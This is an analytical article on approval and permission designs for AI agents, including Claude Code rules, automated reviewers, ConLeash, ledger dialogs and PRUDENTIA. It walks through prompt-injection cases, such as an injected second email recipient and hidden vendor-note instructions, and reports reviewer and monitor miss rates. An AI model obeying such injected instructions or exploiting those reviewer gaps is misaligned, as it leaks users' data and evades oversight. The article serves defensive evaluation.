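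Claude Code now checks file paths more strictly. According to Anthropic's documentation, a rule that allows a folder applies only if both the requested path and the file it leads to match. The editing tools refuse to write to a path that is itself a link. If the automated reviewer is on and a write that no rule allows would leave the project through a linked folder, the user sees a dialog that names the real destination. This is close to what Wiz asked for in July.

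People can also grant standing approvals without fully intending to. A repository can contain allow rules that someone else wrote, and Claude Code applies them once the user agrees to trust the folder. The trust dialog lists the rules, but the user accepts them all with one answer. Until version 2.1.235, users could also approve an action for the rest of the session by accident. This happened if they were typing a comment on a file edit and pressed Shift+Tab to leave the comment field. Claude Code also discarded the comment.

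### Why a rule for Python allows everything

An interpreter is a program that runs code supplied to it, such as `python` for Python or `node` for JavaScript. The rule `Bash(python:*)` lets any shell command that begins with `python` run without a dialog. The rest of the command can name a script or contain the code itself. That code can read files, delete them, send them over the network or start any other program on the machine. The rule therefore lets the agent do anything the user's account can do, even though it names only one program.

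Allowing only one named script is safer, but an agent that can edit files in the project can change the script before running it.

Some programs that don't look like interpreters cause the same problem. Anthropic warns that `devbox run`, `npx` and `docker exec`, which developers use to run programs in a prepared environment, execute whatever command follows them. A rule that allows `devbox run *` therefore also allows a command that deletes the current folder. Anthropic recommends including the inner command in the rule, as in `devbox run npm test`. The version control tool `git` also has an option that makes it run another program.

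Claude Code guards against a few of these cases. For example, it still asks for approval before the file-search program `find` deletes anything, even if the user has allowed every command beginning with `find`. But this protection depends on a list of risky programs, and Anthropic acknowledges that any such list will be incomplete.

### How many users have such rules

Broad rules are common. Anthropic reports that in June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users of Claude Code had written a rule allowing some shell commands. It also reports that 5% allowed any shell command and another 43% had interpreter rules, which it considers "essentially equivalent in practice" to allowing any command.

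If all three percentages are shares of active users, about 97% of the people who wrote a rule had in effect allowed everything. Anthropic's sentence could also mean that the 5% and 43% are shares of the people who wrote a rule, which would be about 24% of active users. Either way, a large group had turned off approval dialogs for the commands that could do the most damage. The share was growing by roughly five percentage points every five weeks.

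Claude Code offers to save a rule only when its dialog can show everything the rule would allow, so people probably wrote the broadest rules by hand rather than approving them with a careless click. They presumably did so after answering many dialogs about Python scripts. Better wording on the "don't ask again" button would do little to help these users.

In figures from June, Anthropic reports that 62% of users had either turned on bypass mode, which removes nearly all dialogs and safety checks, or chosen "don't ask again" for a shell command. The figure is a poor measure of risk because it counts a developer who once saved a rule for `npm test` the same as one who turned on bypass mode.

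The last figure, that 25% of interactive sessions started in bypass mode, is more informative. Some of those sessions may have been safe, since Anthropic advises people to use the mode only in isolated environments where the agent can't cause damage. It doesn't report how many people followed that advice. But if attacks were spread evenly over sessions, a quarter of the attacks would trigger almost no dialogs. Even if all the remaining attacks triggered one, a catch rate of 13.6% would stop only about 10% of all attacks.

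### Saved rules and the automated reviewer

The June figures predate Anthropic's change of default. According to Anthropic's current documentation, interactive Claude Code sessions in a terminal or VS Code usually start in auto mode, in which the automated reviewer decides what to allow. Claude Code sets aside some rules when it enters auto mode, including those that allow the whole shell, any interpreter command, or any command run through a package manager. Otherwise, these rules would let the most dangerous commands run without review.

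The old rules come back when the user leaves auto mode. A developer might follow Anthropic's advice and switch to manual approval for a high-stakes change. If she once allowed `python`, her agent's Python commands will then run without a dialog or automated review, so she has less protection from those commands than she had in auto mode.

Narrower rules stay in force in auto mode, and Claude Code applies them before it sends a call to the reviewer. The documentation lists exceptions, such as writes to protected files and tools whose makers require the user's consent, but an ordinary mail tool isn't among them. If Ruth had allowed `send_email` in Claude Code and then moved to auto mode, the call with the second address would reach neither her nor the reviewer, so the reviewer's 89% catch rate wouldn't apply to it.

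The reviewer can also treat a single approval as standing permission. In a test that Anthropic published in March 2026, it let through 17% of 52 actions in which Claude had actually gone beyond what an employee wanted. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented, for instance because she had approved something similar earlier. The 17% amounts to about nine misses, so the pattern rests on very few examples.

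Anthropic's current rules for consent given in conversation are stricter than those for most saved approvals. To unblock a dangerous action, the user has to name the action and the detail that makes it dangerous, such as which branch of the code the agent may overwrite. If the user tells Claude "you can force-push" without naming the branch, the action stays blocked. Permission normally covers one action, unless the user says it should last. A mail tool that worked this way would let Ruth approve sending the report to Tomas without also approving other recipients.

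### Fifty sessions replayed

Whether tool-level approvals matter in practice depends on how often agents go beyond what the user first approved. Li and colleagues collected 50 working sessions, containing 1,435 tool calls, from six developers at two companies. The developers used GitHub Copilot in the VS Code editor with MCP tools for browsing, files, notes and code repositories.

The researchers described each call by where its data came from and went, whether the data was sensitive, and what the call did, such as reading, writing, deleting or running code. Locations are nested, so approval for a folder covers the files in it but not the rest of the machine. A call counted as a crossing if it fell outside the approved scope on any of these points. For example, approval to read one file in a sales folder could extend to reading other files there, but not to deleting them.

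By this definition, 291 of the 1,435 calls were crossings, or about one in five. The team then replayed the sessions under different approval systems to see which crossings each would have stopped or referred to the user:

| Approval system | Crossings caught | Share of 291 |
|---|---:|---:|
| "Always allow" for a server | 0 | 0% |
| "Always allow" for a tool | 0 | 0% |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 6 | 2.1% |
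| ConLeash | 278 | 95.5% |

The two zeros follow from the definition, because once someone has permanently allowed a tool, the host never asks about it again and so can't catch anything. The more useful result is that there was something to catch nearly six times in an average session of 29 calls.

Auto mode approved 1,428 of the calls and blocked seven, six of which were crossings. Those six were obviously dangerous calls, such as a command that shuts down other running programs. Li and colleagues don't regard the low score as a defect because, as they see it, auto mode judges whether an action is risky in itself, while their own system, ConLeash, checks whether the action goes beyond what the user has already approved.

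In one example, an agent worked in one project and then deleted a folder in another. Auto mode allowed the deletion as an ordinary operation on local files. ConLeash would have prompted the user for approval, because the user had approved work only in the first project.

The distinction is less clear than Li and colleagues suggest. Anthropic also instructs its reviewer to consider what the user asked for, and to treat anything the agent decides on its own as unauthorised. According to its current documentation, auto mode allows local file operations by default only within the working directory, and the reviewer is told to block actions that irreversibly destroy files that existed before the session, so today it might block the deletion in the second project. But auto mode keeps no record of the scope a person approved in earlier dialogs, which is what the replay measured.

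A crossing isn't necessarily harmful. Nobody attacked these developers, and many of the 291 calls were probably a normal part of the work. Li and colleagues don't report how many the developers would have refused. The researchers labelled the calls using ConLeash's own definition of scope, which favours ConLeash in the comparison. Six developers are also too few to establish how often agents elsewhere go beyond an approval.

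The replay may miss changes like the one in Ruth's email. The basic labels distinguish the local machine, the internal network and the public internet. Tomas's mailbox and the stranger's would probably both count as public internet, so adding the stranger's address would not count as a crossing. ConLeash can also limit an approval to particular recipients, but the count of 291 appears to be based on the basic labels.

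### Five commercial agents

Michael and Roesner's mid-2026 tests also show how differently companies handle saved approvals. The researchers gave each agent limited access, such as to a Gmail account created for the study or a desktop folder, and asked it to do tasks under every available setting. They then withdrew the access and tried again, except in ChatGPT's agent mode, which had no permissions to grant.

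| Agent | Choices offered | Withdrawing an approval | What ran without a dialog |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude chatbot | "Always allow", "Needs approval" or "Blocked" | Change the setting or disconnect the tool | A Gmail draft, under "Needs approval" |
| Claude Cowork | Access to a folder, such as to read or delete files | Not possible in the app | Later actions in the approved folder |
| ChatGPT, chat mode | Approve or refuse each action | Nothing saved to withdraw | No action that had a permission setting |
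| ChatGPT, agent mode | None | Nothing to withdraw | Actions in the remote browser, such as opening Gmail |
| Codex | Approve each action, or automatic review | Switch off automatic review at any time | Whatever the automatic reviewer allowed |

Michael and Roesner reproduced the Gmail draft incident at least three times in June and July, and reported it to Anthropic on 2 July. When they asked Claude why it hadn't waited for approval, it claimed to have inferred permission from their request. A model's account of its own behaviour is weak evidence, though this one is consistent with the browser log. Users had no setting to prevent this other than disabling the tool.

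Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, had the most serious problem with withdrawing permission. Once users let it delete files in a folder, they could not revoke that permission. A warning in the dialog implied that starting a new task would end it. New sessions did start without the permission, but the old session stayed in the app's history and still had it if someone reopened the session. The researchers found no reliable remedy except the operating system's controls, where available, or uninstalling the app.

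In Codex, the user could turn automatic review on or off only for the whole session, so someone who wanted it for routine file edits had to accept it for every other tool as well.

ChatGPT's chat mode, the strictest of the five, would protect Ruth from an "Always allow" setting she had forgotten, but would show her many more dialogs. Michael and Roesner argue that companies force users to choose between constant prompts and automated decisions they can barely see or control.

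Academic designs are no better at letting users withdraw permissions. Michael and Roesner reviewed 21 proposed permission systems and found only six that clearly let users change or revoke a permission after setting it. Two of those six allow this only between sessions.

In October 2026, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default for new sessions in most Claude apps on its Pro, Max and Team plans, so many people who would have seen dialogs in June no longer will. Claude Code, which was not among the five, has a better way to withdraw approvals. Typing `/permissions` lists every rule and the file it comes from, and deleting a rule takes effect from the agent's next tool call, even in the middle of a task, but the user still has to remember to check for rules to delete.

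### Approvals that expire

For several years, phones have offered approvals that expire automatically. Apple added an "Allow Once" option for location access to the iPhone in 2019. A year later, Android introduced "Only this time" for location, the camera and the microphone, and began withdrawing sensitive permissions from apps that people had not opened for a few months.

On Android, an app given location access "once" can read the location repeatedly until shortly after the user leaves the app. Anthropic describes "Allow this action" in Claude's browser extension more narrowly, as permission for a single action, after which Claude asks again. The closest match to Android's version is Claude Code's approval of file edits for one session. However, an agent's session can run for hours unattended, while someone using a map app usually has it open in front of her.

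Expiry limits the damage from approvals that people have forgotten. It would have fixed the old Cowork sessions that kept their access to a folder. It does much less for someone who uses a tool every day. Android's rule for unused apps, for instance, would never apply to them. Suppose Ruth's approval for `send_email` expires each night and her agent sends 20 emails a day. She sees a dialog for the first email each morning and chooses "Allow for today". The other 19 go out without her seeing them, so expiry adds a check on only 5% of her email.

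Agents also have few ways to set such limits. Li and colleagues acknowledge that even ConLeash's rules can't express "allow for today".

A one-time choice helps only if it is as easy to find as the permanent one. When Claude first tries to read a file outside the project in auto mode, Claude Code lets the user answer yes or no, either permanently or only for now. A user with just one file in mind may choose the permanent yes, which allows reads anywhere on the machine that their other settings permit and stops the question from appearing again.

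### When a saved approval is worth having

Refusing every standing approval has a cost too, because it means more dialogs and perhaps less attention to each. A simple comparison shows when saving some approvals would help. Let *c₀* be the catch rate of someone who answers every dialog, *c₁* her catch rate on the dialogs that remain after she has saved some approvals, and *s* the share of attacks that fall on calls she no longer sees. Saving approvals stops more attacks overall if:

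(1 − s) × c₁ > c₀

Anthropic's testers caught 17% of attacks early in a session and 5% later. If saved approvals kept a person at 17% when she would otherwise have fallen to 5%, she would catch more attacks overall as long as fewer than about 71% of them fell on the calls she had always allowed. This is the most favourable case, because it assumes that the number of dialogs caused the whole decline. In Yan's experiment, fewer dialogs did not help.

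The inequality depends mostly on *s*, which varies widely between approvals. Few attacks would need a rule that lets the agent list the files in a project, so allowing that adds almost no risk. A rule for `python` covers nearly anything an attacker might do through the shell. Ruth's approval of `send_email` removes only one kind of dialog, but it is the one she would need to see in any attack that emails her files out.

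## Tests of changed approval designs

If Ruth deletes her saved approval for `send_email`, every email produces a dialog again, and she has to spot the second address among dozens of harmless ones. Designers have looked for alternatives to showing no dialogs or too many. Some change what the dialog shows, some have software decide which calls need one, and some let software answer in the person's place. Many tests of these designs count the interruptions avoided, which is easier than finding out whether people catch more attacks.

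### Drawing attention to the right field

A host can counter habituation by varying how its dialogs look. In the three-week app-store experiment, students whose warnings kept changing appearance retained more of their initial caution than students whose warnings always looked the same. But a new colour or layout draws attention only to the dialog as a whole. Ruth might look up, see the email to Tomas that she asked for, and click "Allow" as before.

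A host can also require an action before it accepts an approval. The action has to involve the value itself, or people will complete it without reading the value, as many of the bank customers did when they had to open a text message for their code. If the dialog made Ruth click each recipient before it enabled "Allow", she would at least get past the first name, though the clicking could become a habit too.

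Either method might make people refuse more calls without understanding them any better. When nearly every call is safe, most of those extra refusals would block safe calls. A useful test therefore measures how well people understand the calls and how often they refuse both safe and dangerous ones.

### Four dialogs for the same requests

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, measured all of these with 80 unpaid volunteers. In their main example, an agent has to reconcile supplier invoices and send an auditor only the summary totals. Instructions hidden in a vendor's note lead the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and it then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name are all acceptable, and only the file's history shows that the email would break the user's restriction.

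Hossain and colleagues call this a cumulative violation. A local violation is one that people can see in the call itself, such as a transfer to a forbidden recipient. The volunteers judged both kinds in scenarios involving email, shared documents and purchasing. Each volunteer used one of four dialogs and made 12 decisions, half of them about malicious requests.

| Dialog | What it shows | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests refused | Comprehension | Median time |
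|---|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Conventional | A short description of the action | 55.0% | 8.3% | 57.1% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments | The description and the tool's arguments | 43.3% | 10.0% | 67.9% | 23.4 s |
| Chronological log | The arguments, the user's original instructions and every earlier step in order | 32.5% | 12.5% | 76.7% | 38.6 s |
| Ledger | The same facts as the log, arranged around the effect of the action | 24.2% | 14.2% | 81.7% | 33.2 s |

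The first two rows give an estimate of how much a more faithful display helps. People approved 52 of 120 unsafe requests with the arguments on the screen, compared with 66 without them. It is plausible that showing the arguments reduces unsafe approvals, but this evidence is weak. A gap of that size could just about be chance even if all the decisions were independent, and they weren't, because the decisions for each dialog came from only 20 people.

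The ledger is the design that Hossain and colleagues propose. It quotes the user's restriction word for word, lists the exact pending action from the system's own records, and states the combined effect of that action and the steps before it. It also links the statement to the recorded events, so that the reader can check it. A similar dialog for Ruth's email might look like this:

```text
You wrote:        "Email the quarterly report to my colleague Tomas."

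History:          E01  Read notes/plan.md
                  E02  Read notes/supplier-update.pdf

Pending action:   send_email
                  quarterly-report.pdf
                  to tomas@example.com, reports@example.net

Combined effect:  The quarterly report would go to two addresses.

[Inspect events]   [Allow]   [Refuse]
```

The last statement doesn't label the email a violation. Hossain and colleagues also left verdicts out of the ledger in their experiment, so that it would contain no more information than the log. The comparison therefore tested only how the information was arranged. After adjustment, the approval rate for unsafe requests was 7.9 percentage points lower with the ledger than with the log, but the result is uncertain, with a 95% interval from 19.7 points lower to 3.8 points higher. People were also about five seconds faster with the ledger.

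### Better judgement or more refusals

People refused more safe requests as the dialogs grew more detailed, so part of the improvement could come from a general readiness to refuse. Signal detection theory can separate this readiness from the ability to tell safe requests from unsafe ones. By the earlier formula, sensitivity rises from about 1.3 with the conventional dialog to 1.8 with the ledger, while the criterion falls from about 0.75 to 0.19.

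Better judgement accounts for roughly three-fifths of the ledger group's improvement in catching unsafe requests. The ledger group caught 76% of them, compared with 45% for people with the conventional dialog. If the conventional group had refused 14.2% of safe requests, as the ledger group did, but had been no better at telling safe requests from unsafe ones, it would have caught about 57% of the unsafe ones. The comprehension scores also support the conclusion that judgement improved.

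These rates would probably be lower at work. Half of the requests in the study were malicious, and reviewing them was the volunteers' whole task for about 20 minutes. The researchers expect habituation to matter most when violations are rare. The ledger also takes about twice as long to review as the conventional dialog. At 33 seconds each, 100 dialogs a day would take 55 minutes, and an impatient user would save that time by not reading them.

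### The nearest figure for an altered value

The local violations in this study are the closest match to Ruth's email. People caught 33 of 40 (83%) with the ledger and 30 of 40 (75%) with the log. Those rates are encouraging compared with the 13.6% from Anthropic's experiment, but this study's conditions were much easier.

It still isn't the catch rate for an injected argument. The local violations include a transfer to a prohibited recipient, which the reader can recognise by checking the call against a written restriction. Ruth named one recipient but wrote no restriction against others. Hossain and colleagues also don't report local violations separately for the two simpler dialogs, so their figures can't show how much seeing the arguments helped people notice a bad one. None of the tests described in this section takes a call that the user expects, alters one value, and compares how often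 people notice the change under an ordinary dialog and an improved one.

The ledger had no visible benefit when a violation depended on several linked steps. People approved 7 of 30 such requests with the ledger and 7 of 30 with the log. Hossain and colleagues suspect that one sentence is too short to explain a file that has passed through several others.

### The software behind the ledger

In the user study, the researchers made sure the ledger's statements were correct. A working host would have to produce those statements itself, so the team also tested a monitor that records each tool call and tracks which sources each file came from. If the agent builds a file from several sources, the monitor treats the new file as possibly containing data from all of them.

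The monitor detected 107 of 120 violations (89.2%) and raised five false alerts on 120 safe actions. It caught 38 of 40 local violations (95%), a larger share than people caught with the best dialog, though on a different set of cases. If software can check a value against a written restriction that reliably, there is little reason for a host to leave the check to a person.

Without the user's own restriction, the monitor detected only 30 of the 80 cumulative violations, down from 69, and its false alerts rose from 5 to 15. A general warning that "this action sends data outside" is therefore a weak substitute for knowing what the user wanted.

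The researchers then let the monitor block actions on its own. Two small open models, working as agents, carried out unauthorised actions in 52 and 58 of 120 malicious runs without the monitor, and in 6 and 7 with it. With the monitor, each also finished four fewer of 120 harmless tasks. In these runs, the monitor could see everything the agent did. When it saw only part, and blocked whatever it couldn't assess, the share of harmless tasks completed fell to 76.7%.

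### How ConLeash decides when to ask

A better dialog does nothing for calls that a saved approval lets through. ConLeash, the permission system by Li and colleagues, replaces "Always allow this tool" with approvals that have limits, and asks again when a call exceeds them. It sits between the host and the MCP servers and works as follows:

1. The user can state firm limits in ordinary language, such as never sending files from outside the project to external recipients. A model translates each one into a formal rule, which later approvals can't override.
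2. When the agent makes a call, ConLeash describes it by the four properties used in the replay of 50 sessions: the data's source, destination and sensitivity, and the call's effects.
3. It compares this description with the user's limits and earlier approvals.
4. It blocks a call that breaks a firm limit and allows one that falls inside an earlier approval. If no approval covers the call, or the most specific rules conflict, it asks.
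5. When it asks, it offers approvals of different widths and saves the user's choice as a new rule.

The comparison in the third step needs every property to fit:

call fits approval ⇔ source ⊑ source′ and destination ⊑ destination′ and sensitivity ⊑ sensitivity′ and effects ⊑ effects′

The symbol ⊑ means "falls within", as a file falls within its folder, and the marked terms belong to the earlier approval.

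ConLeash tracks sensitive data from one call to the next. If an agent compresses a sensitive file and then tries to email the archive, ConLeash still treats the archive as sensitive. When it can't predict a program's effects, it marks the program's output as sensitive regardless of the input.

When Ruth's agent first asks to email Tomas a file from her finance folder, ConLeash might offer these choices:

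```text
Allow once
Always allow:  this file, to tomas@example.com
Always allow:  files in /home/ruth/finance, to tomas@example.com
Always allow:  any local file, to any outside address
```

The second or third choice would bring back a dialog when `reports@example.net` appeared, but the last would not, because both mailboxes are outside addresses. Ruth's protection therefore depends on which one she picks when nothing is wrong and on whether she reads any later dialog.

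### The ConLeash benchmark

Li and colleagues built a benchmark of 984 sequences of tool calls, with 3,538 steps in all, for 13 real MCP servers. A model generated the sequences and the researchers reviewed them. Of the sequences, 203 stayed within what the user had approved, 640 went beyond it, and 141 broke a firm limit.

ConLeash made the right decision at 98.2% of the steps. It let 98.3% of harmless calls through without a dialog, and blocked or asked the user about 99.4% of those that went too far. But errors accumulate over a session, and ConLeash got every step right in only 82.6% of sequences that used several servers. Most of its mistakes were unnecessary questions, which annoy users but don't breach security.

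The correct answers came from simulating the same consent process that ConLeash follows, so the score mainly measures how well the software applies its own scheme. It isn't evidence that the scheme matches what users would want.

The model that translates calls and limits into formal terms is the part most likely to fail. A logic solver then makes the decision, and it always gives the same answer for the same description. That guarantee covers only the description, so if the model describes a call wrongly, the solver's decision won't be about the actual call. Li and colleagues report that the solver adds 8.2 milliseconds per call and the model adds another 4.69 seconds, unless its work has been done beforehand.

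One type of violation that ConLeash missed is close to Ruth's problem. It couldn't enforce "never add external attendees to calendar events" because its rule language couldn't distinguish internal email domains from external ones. But in the user study, it could handle a rule that named the domain, such as allowing email only to addresses at a particular company. Ruth would be safer telling it "only email people at example.com" than "don't email outsiders".

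### Sixteen people try it

Li and colleagues then had 16 people use both ConLeash and a conventional dialog with "Allow", "Deny" and "Always Allow". Each person did three tasks with each system, and the order varied. People chose a lasting approval in 46.3% of their decisions with ConLeash, compared with 13.3% with the conventional dialog. ConLeash attached a limit to every lasting approval, so the higher rate is less alarming than it would be if the approvals were equally broad. Saved approvals let 41.9% of calls run without a question.

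Participants also wrote three firm limits each, and ConLeash enforced 45 of the 48. The failures came from vague wording, such as "don't touch my photos". Fifteen people preferred ConLeash and one had no preference. When the researchers described a case where an automated reviewer would approve an action but ConLeash would ask, all 16 preferred ConLeash's approach.

The study measured which approvals people choose and which system they like, but not whether they notice an injected argument when the dialog appears. Preference is probably as poor a guide to noticing as the feeling of control was in Yan's experiment.

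### Deciding before the agent starts

Having people write rules in advance is a simpler way to reduce dialogs. In Yan's experiment, this cut the number from 18 to 10.9 per person but saved little time in such a short session. People who wrote rules spent 129 seconds on rules and dialogs together, compared with 142 seconds for those who answered every dialog, and the difference could be due to chance.

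Every private-data request in the experiment went beyond the task, so a "never" rule would have blocked them all without hindering it. Only 10 of 35 people chose that rule, while 23 chose "ask" and two chose "allow". Choosing "ask" was understandable because people couldn't know in advance what requests would come.

Yan suggests that the system could instead learn narrower rules from people's answers, but didn't test this. If someone keeps approving messages to one recipient, the host could offer to stop asking about that recipient but still ask about new ones. This would suit Ruth well, because legitimate emails to Tomas would no longer interrupt her and the stranger's address would stand out.

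Categories based on tools alone can't make that distinction. Yan also built a program that used a model to sort tools by their names, descriptions and input formats. In a simulation of "never" rules, the program failed to stop 14% of the tools it should have blocked. It sorted tools only by what they could do, so it would have treated an email to Tomas and an email to a stranger the same way.

Another option is to predict the user's answer. Wu and colleagues, who ran the permission study with 205 people, argue that a good predictor could greatly reduce how many decisions people make. They would still send uncertain cases to the user, and let her correct mistakes and withdraw earlier permissions. However, predictions work best for repeated choices. Ruth's past approvals of email to Tomas are no basis for predicting whether she would approve email to an address she has never seen.

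*Security, Privacy, and Safety for Agentic AI Systems*, from the UW Security and Privacy Research Lab, describes Janus, a shared framework for comparing approval designs before recruiting participants. The lab and its collaborators used it to evaluate six permission assistants with simulated users. Simulated users make it easy to try many designs, but they behave only as their makers expect. One assistant turned a single decision into a broader rule, and Yan notes that a rule suited to one case didn't always fit a later one. Janus can help eliminate weak designs, but measuring how often users catch injected arguments requires human participants.

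### Keeping hostile text away from the decision

ConLeash checks whether a call exceeds what the user approved. Information-flow control instead tracks whether untrusted text could have influenced the call. The system labels each piece of data as trusted or untrusted, and anything derived from untrusted data also becomes untrusted.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, used this method in an agent called PRUDENTIA. The system hides untrusted documents from the planning model by storing them under placeholders, which the model can pass to other tools. An action with real consequences can run without approval if the model chose it before seeing anything untrusted. Data can also leave without approval if every recipient is allowed to read it.

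If Ruth's agent worked this way and didn't need the outsider's document to write the email, the hidden instruction would never reach the planner, so the call would contain only Tomas's address. If the planner had to read the document, the planner would lose its trusted status, and an email to someone with no right to read the report would require approval. The host could then give its specific reason for asking in the dialog.

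In older versions of this approach, strict rules cut the share of tasks that agents completed without human help by up to 30% on AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark for agents and prompt injection. PRUDENTIA gives the planner the rules that apply so that the planner can avoid triggering them. PRUDENTIA completed up to 9% more tasks without human help than an earlier system, FIDES, and reduced approvals by a factor of up to 1.9. It needed no approvals on a second benchmark, where no task depended on untrusted content.

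Part of the saving comes from asking the user to endorse content instead of approving each action. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, PRUDENTIA can ask the user once to endorse the email as trustworthy, then treat its contents as trusted and carry out all ten. Kolluri and colleagues count this as one interruption instead of ten.

Endorsing whole documents may be less safe under attack than approving single calls. An approval dialog for a single call at least shows a recipient or a path. To endorse a document, Ruth has to vouch for all of it, and the attacker's instruction may be in a part she doesn't read. If she endorses a document that contains the instruction, she overrides the system's guarantee, and later actions that follow the instruction can run without a dialog.

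Kolluri and colleagues counted approvals on harmless runs and assumed that the person would grant each one. This is a fair way to count interruptions, but it does not measure how many malicious documents people would endorse, which is needed to compare one endorsement with ten approvals.

Another design, the sandbox, restricts what the agent can reach so that fewer actions need approval. Anthropic considers this safe but laborious, because someone has to configure each new capability, and anything that needs the network or the rest of the machine breaks the isolation. A sandbox works well for a test suite that only reads and writes project files, but it helps little with Ruth's email, because she wants the agent to send her report outside the machine.

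### How an automated reviewer decides

Anthropic described the design of Claude Code's automated reviewer in March 2026. Before the agent reads a web page, a file or other outside content, a separate detector scans it and adds a warning if it finds signs of an attack. The agent can make read-only calls and edit files inside the project without further review. A language model examines most other calls.

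The reviewing model sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that a compromised agent can't use them to persuade the reviewer. It also removes the results of earlier calls, because an attacker's text would arrive in them. The reviewer first makes a quick yes-or-no decision, leaning towards blocking, and then reasons through only the calls it flagged.

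The two stages trade misses against false alarms, much as a human reader does:

| | Safe calls blocked | Real overreach missed | Synthetic data theft missed |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes about 95% of the false alarms but more than doubles the share of dangerous calls that get through. Anthropic accepted this because a reviewer that blocked one safe call in 12 would disrupt long tasks too much.

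Ruth's original request names Tomas, but the call has a second recipient she never mentioned. The reviewer receives both the request and the call, and its default rules cover sending data to a service the user never specified, so it has a good chance of blocking the email. A near-copy of Tomas's address is harder to catch. If Ruth wrote only "send it to Tomas" and the agent looked up the address, the reviewer doesn't receive the search result, so it has nothing to compare with `tomas@example.org`. Anthropic acknowledges that removing tool results means the reviewer sometimes can't determine where a value came from.

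After a block, the agent receives the reason and looks for a safer way to continue. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the decision returns to the user. Anthropic has also added a category of actions that the reviewer should never approve, which includes sending confidential data to outsiders. A user who wants to take such an action has to leave auto mode or run the command herself.

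### The third-party tests of August 2026

Anthropic published two outside tests of auto mode when it announced the change of default. In the first, Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, worked with Anthropic for two weeks and inserted artificial attacks into records of real coding sessions. This tests the reviewer directly, because the dangerous action is already in the record and the agent has no chance to resist it.

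Anthropic used some of Apollo's successful attacks to strengthen the reviewer, mainly by giving it more information, such as whether a code repository is public. Apollo then retested the reviewer, including on attacks that Anthropic had not seen. Across both sets of attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

Since that figure includes attacks Anthropic had used to make the improvements, the unseen set is better evidence. On that set, the reviewer caught about half of the attacks it had missed before and missed about 2% of those it had caught before. If it started from a 12% miss rate on that set, the new rate would be about 8%, so the improvement seems real. Anthropic doesn't say how many more safe actions the stronger reviewer blocks. It warns that the attacks were designed to find weaknesses, so 7% isn't the miss rate in ordinary use.

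For the second test, Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to try 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against the Claude models Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 in auto mode. Without the reviewer, only 0.09% of attempts succeeded against the same models, or about two in 2,160 if each model faced all 720. The models' own resistance therefore explains most of the result, since it left the reviewer almost nothing to stop.

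Even with zero successes, the true success rate could be as high as about 0.4% if the 720 attempts were independent. But the attempts repeated 72 scenarios, and if repeated attempts at a scenario tend to have the same result, the upper limit is nearer 4%. The attackers had also tuned their text against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, not the models in the test. An attacker who adapts to the current model and its reviewer might do better.

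The results for OpenAI's Codex are more informative about what a reviewer adds, because its model was easier to attack. GPT-5.6 Sol carried out the injected instructions in 19.03% of attempts with full access and 5.83% with automatic review, a rate about 69% lower. OpenAI has since released a new version of its reviewer. The test used a browser connection made by Trajectory Labs, without the safeguards in either company's own browser extension.

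The details of both results come from Anthropic, which chose to publish them and paid for at least the second. Independent work is less favorable. Yan cites a stress test, AmPermBench, in which automated permission systems missed some actions that exceeded the user's authority when the instructions were deliberately ambiguous. This fits the pattern of mistaken consent in Anthropic's own misses. Vague instructions are common in real work, and an attacker can look for sessions where the user's instructions are vague enough to seem to cover an extra recipient.
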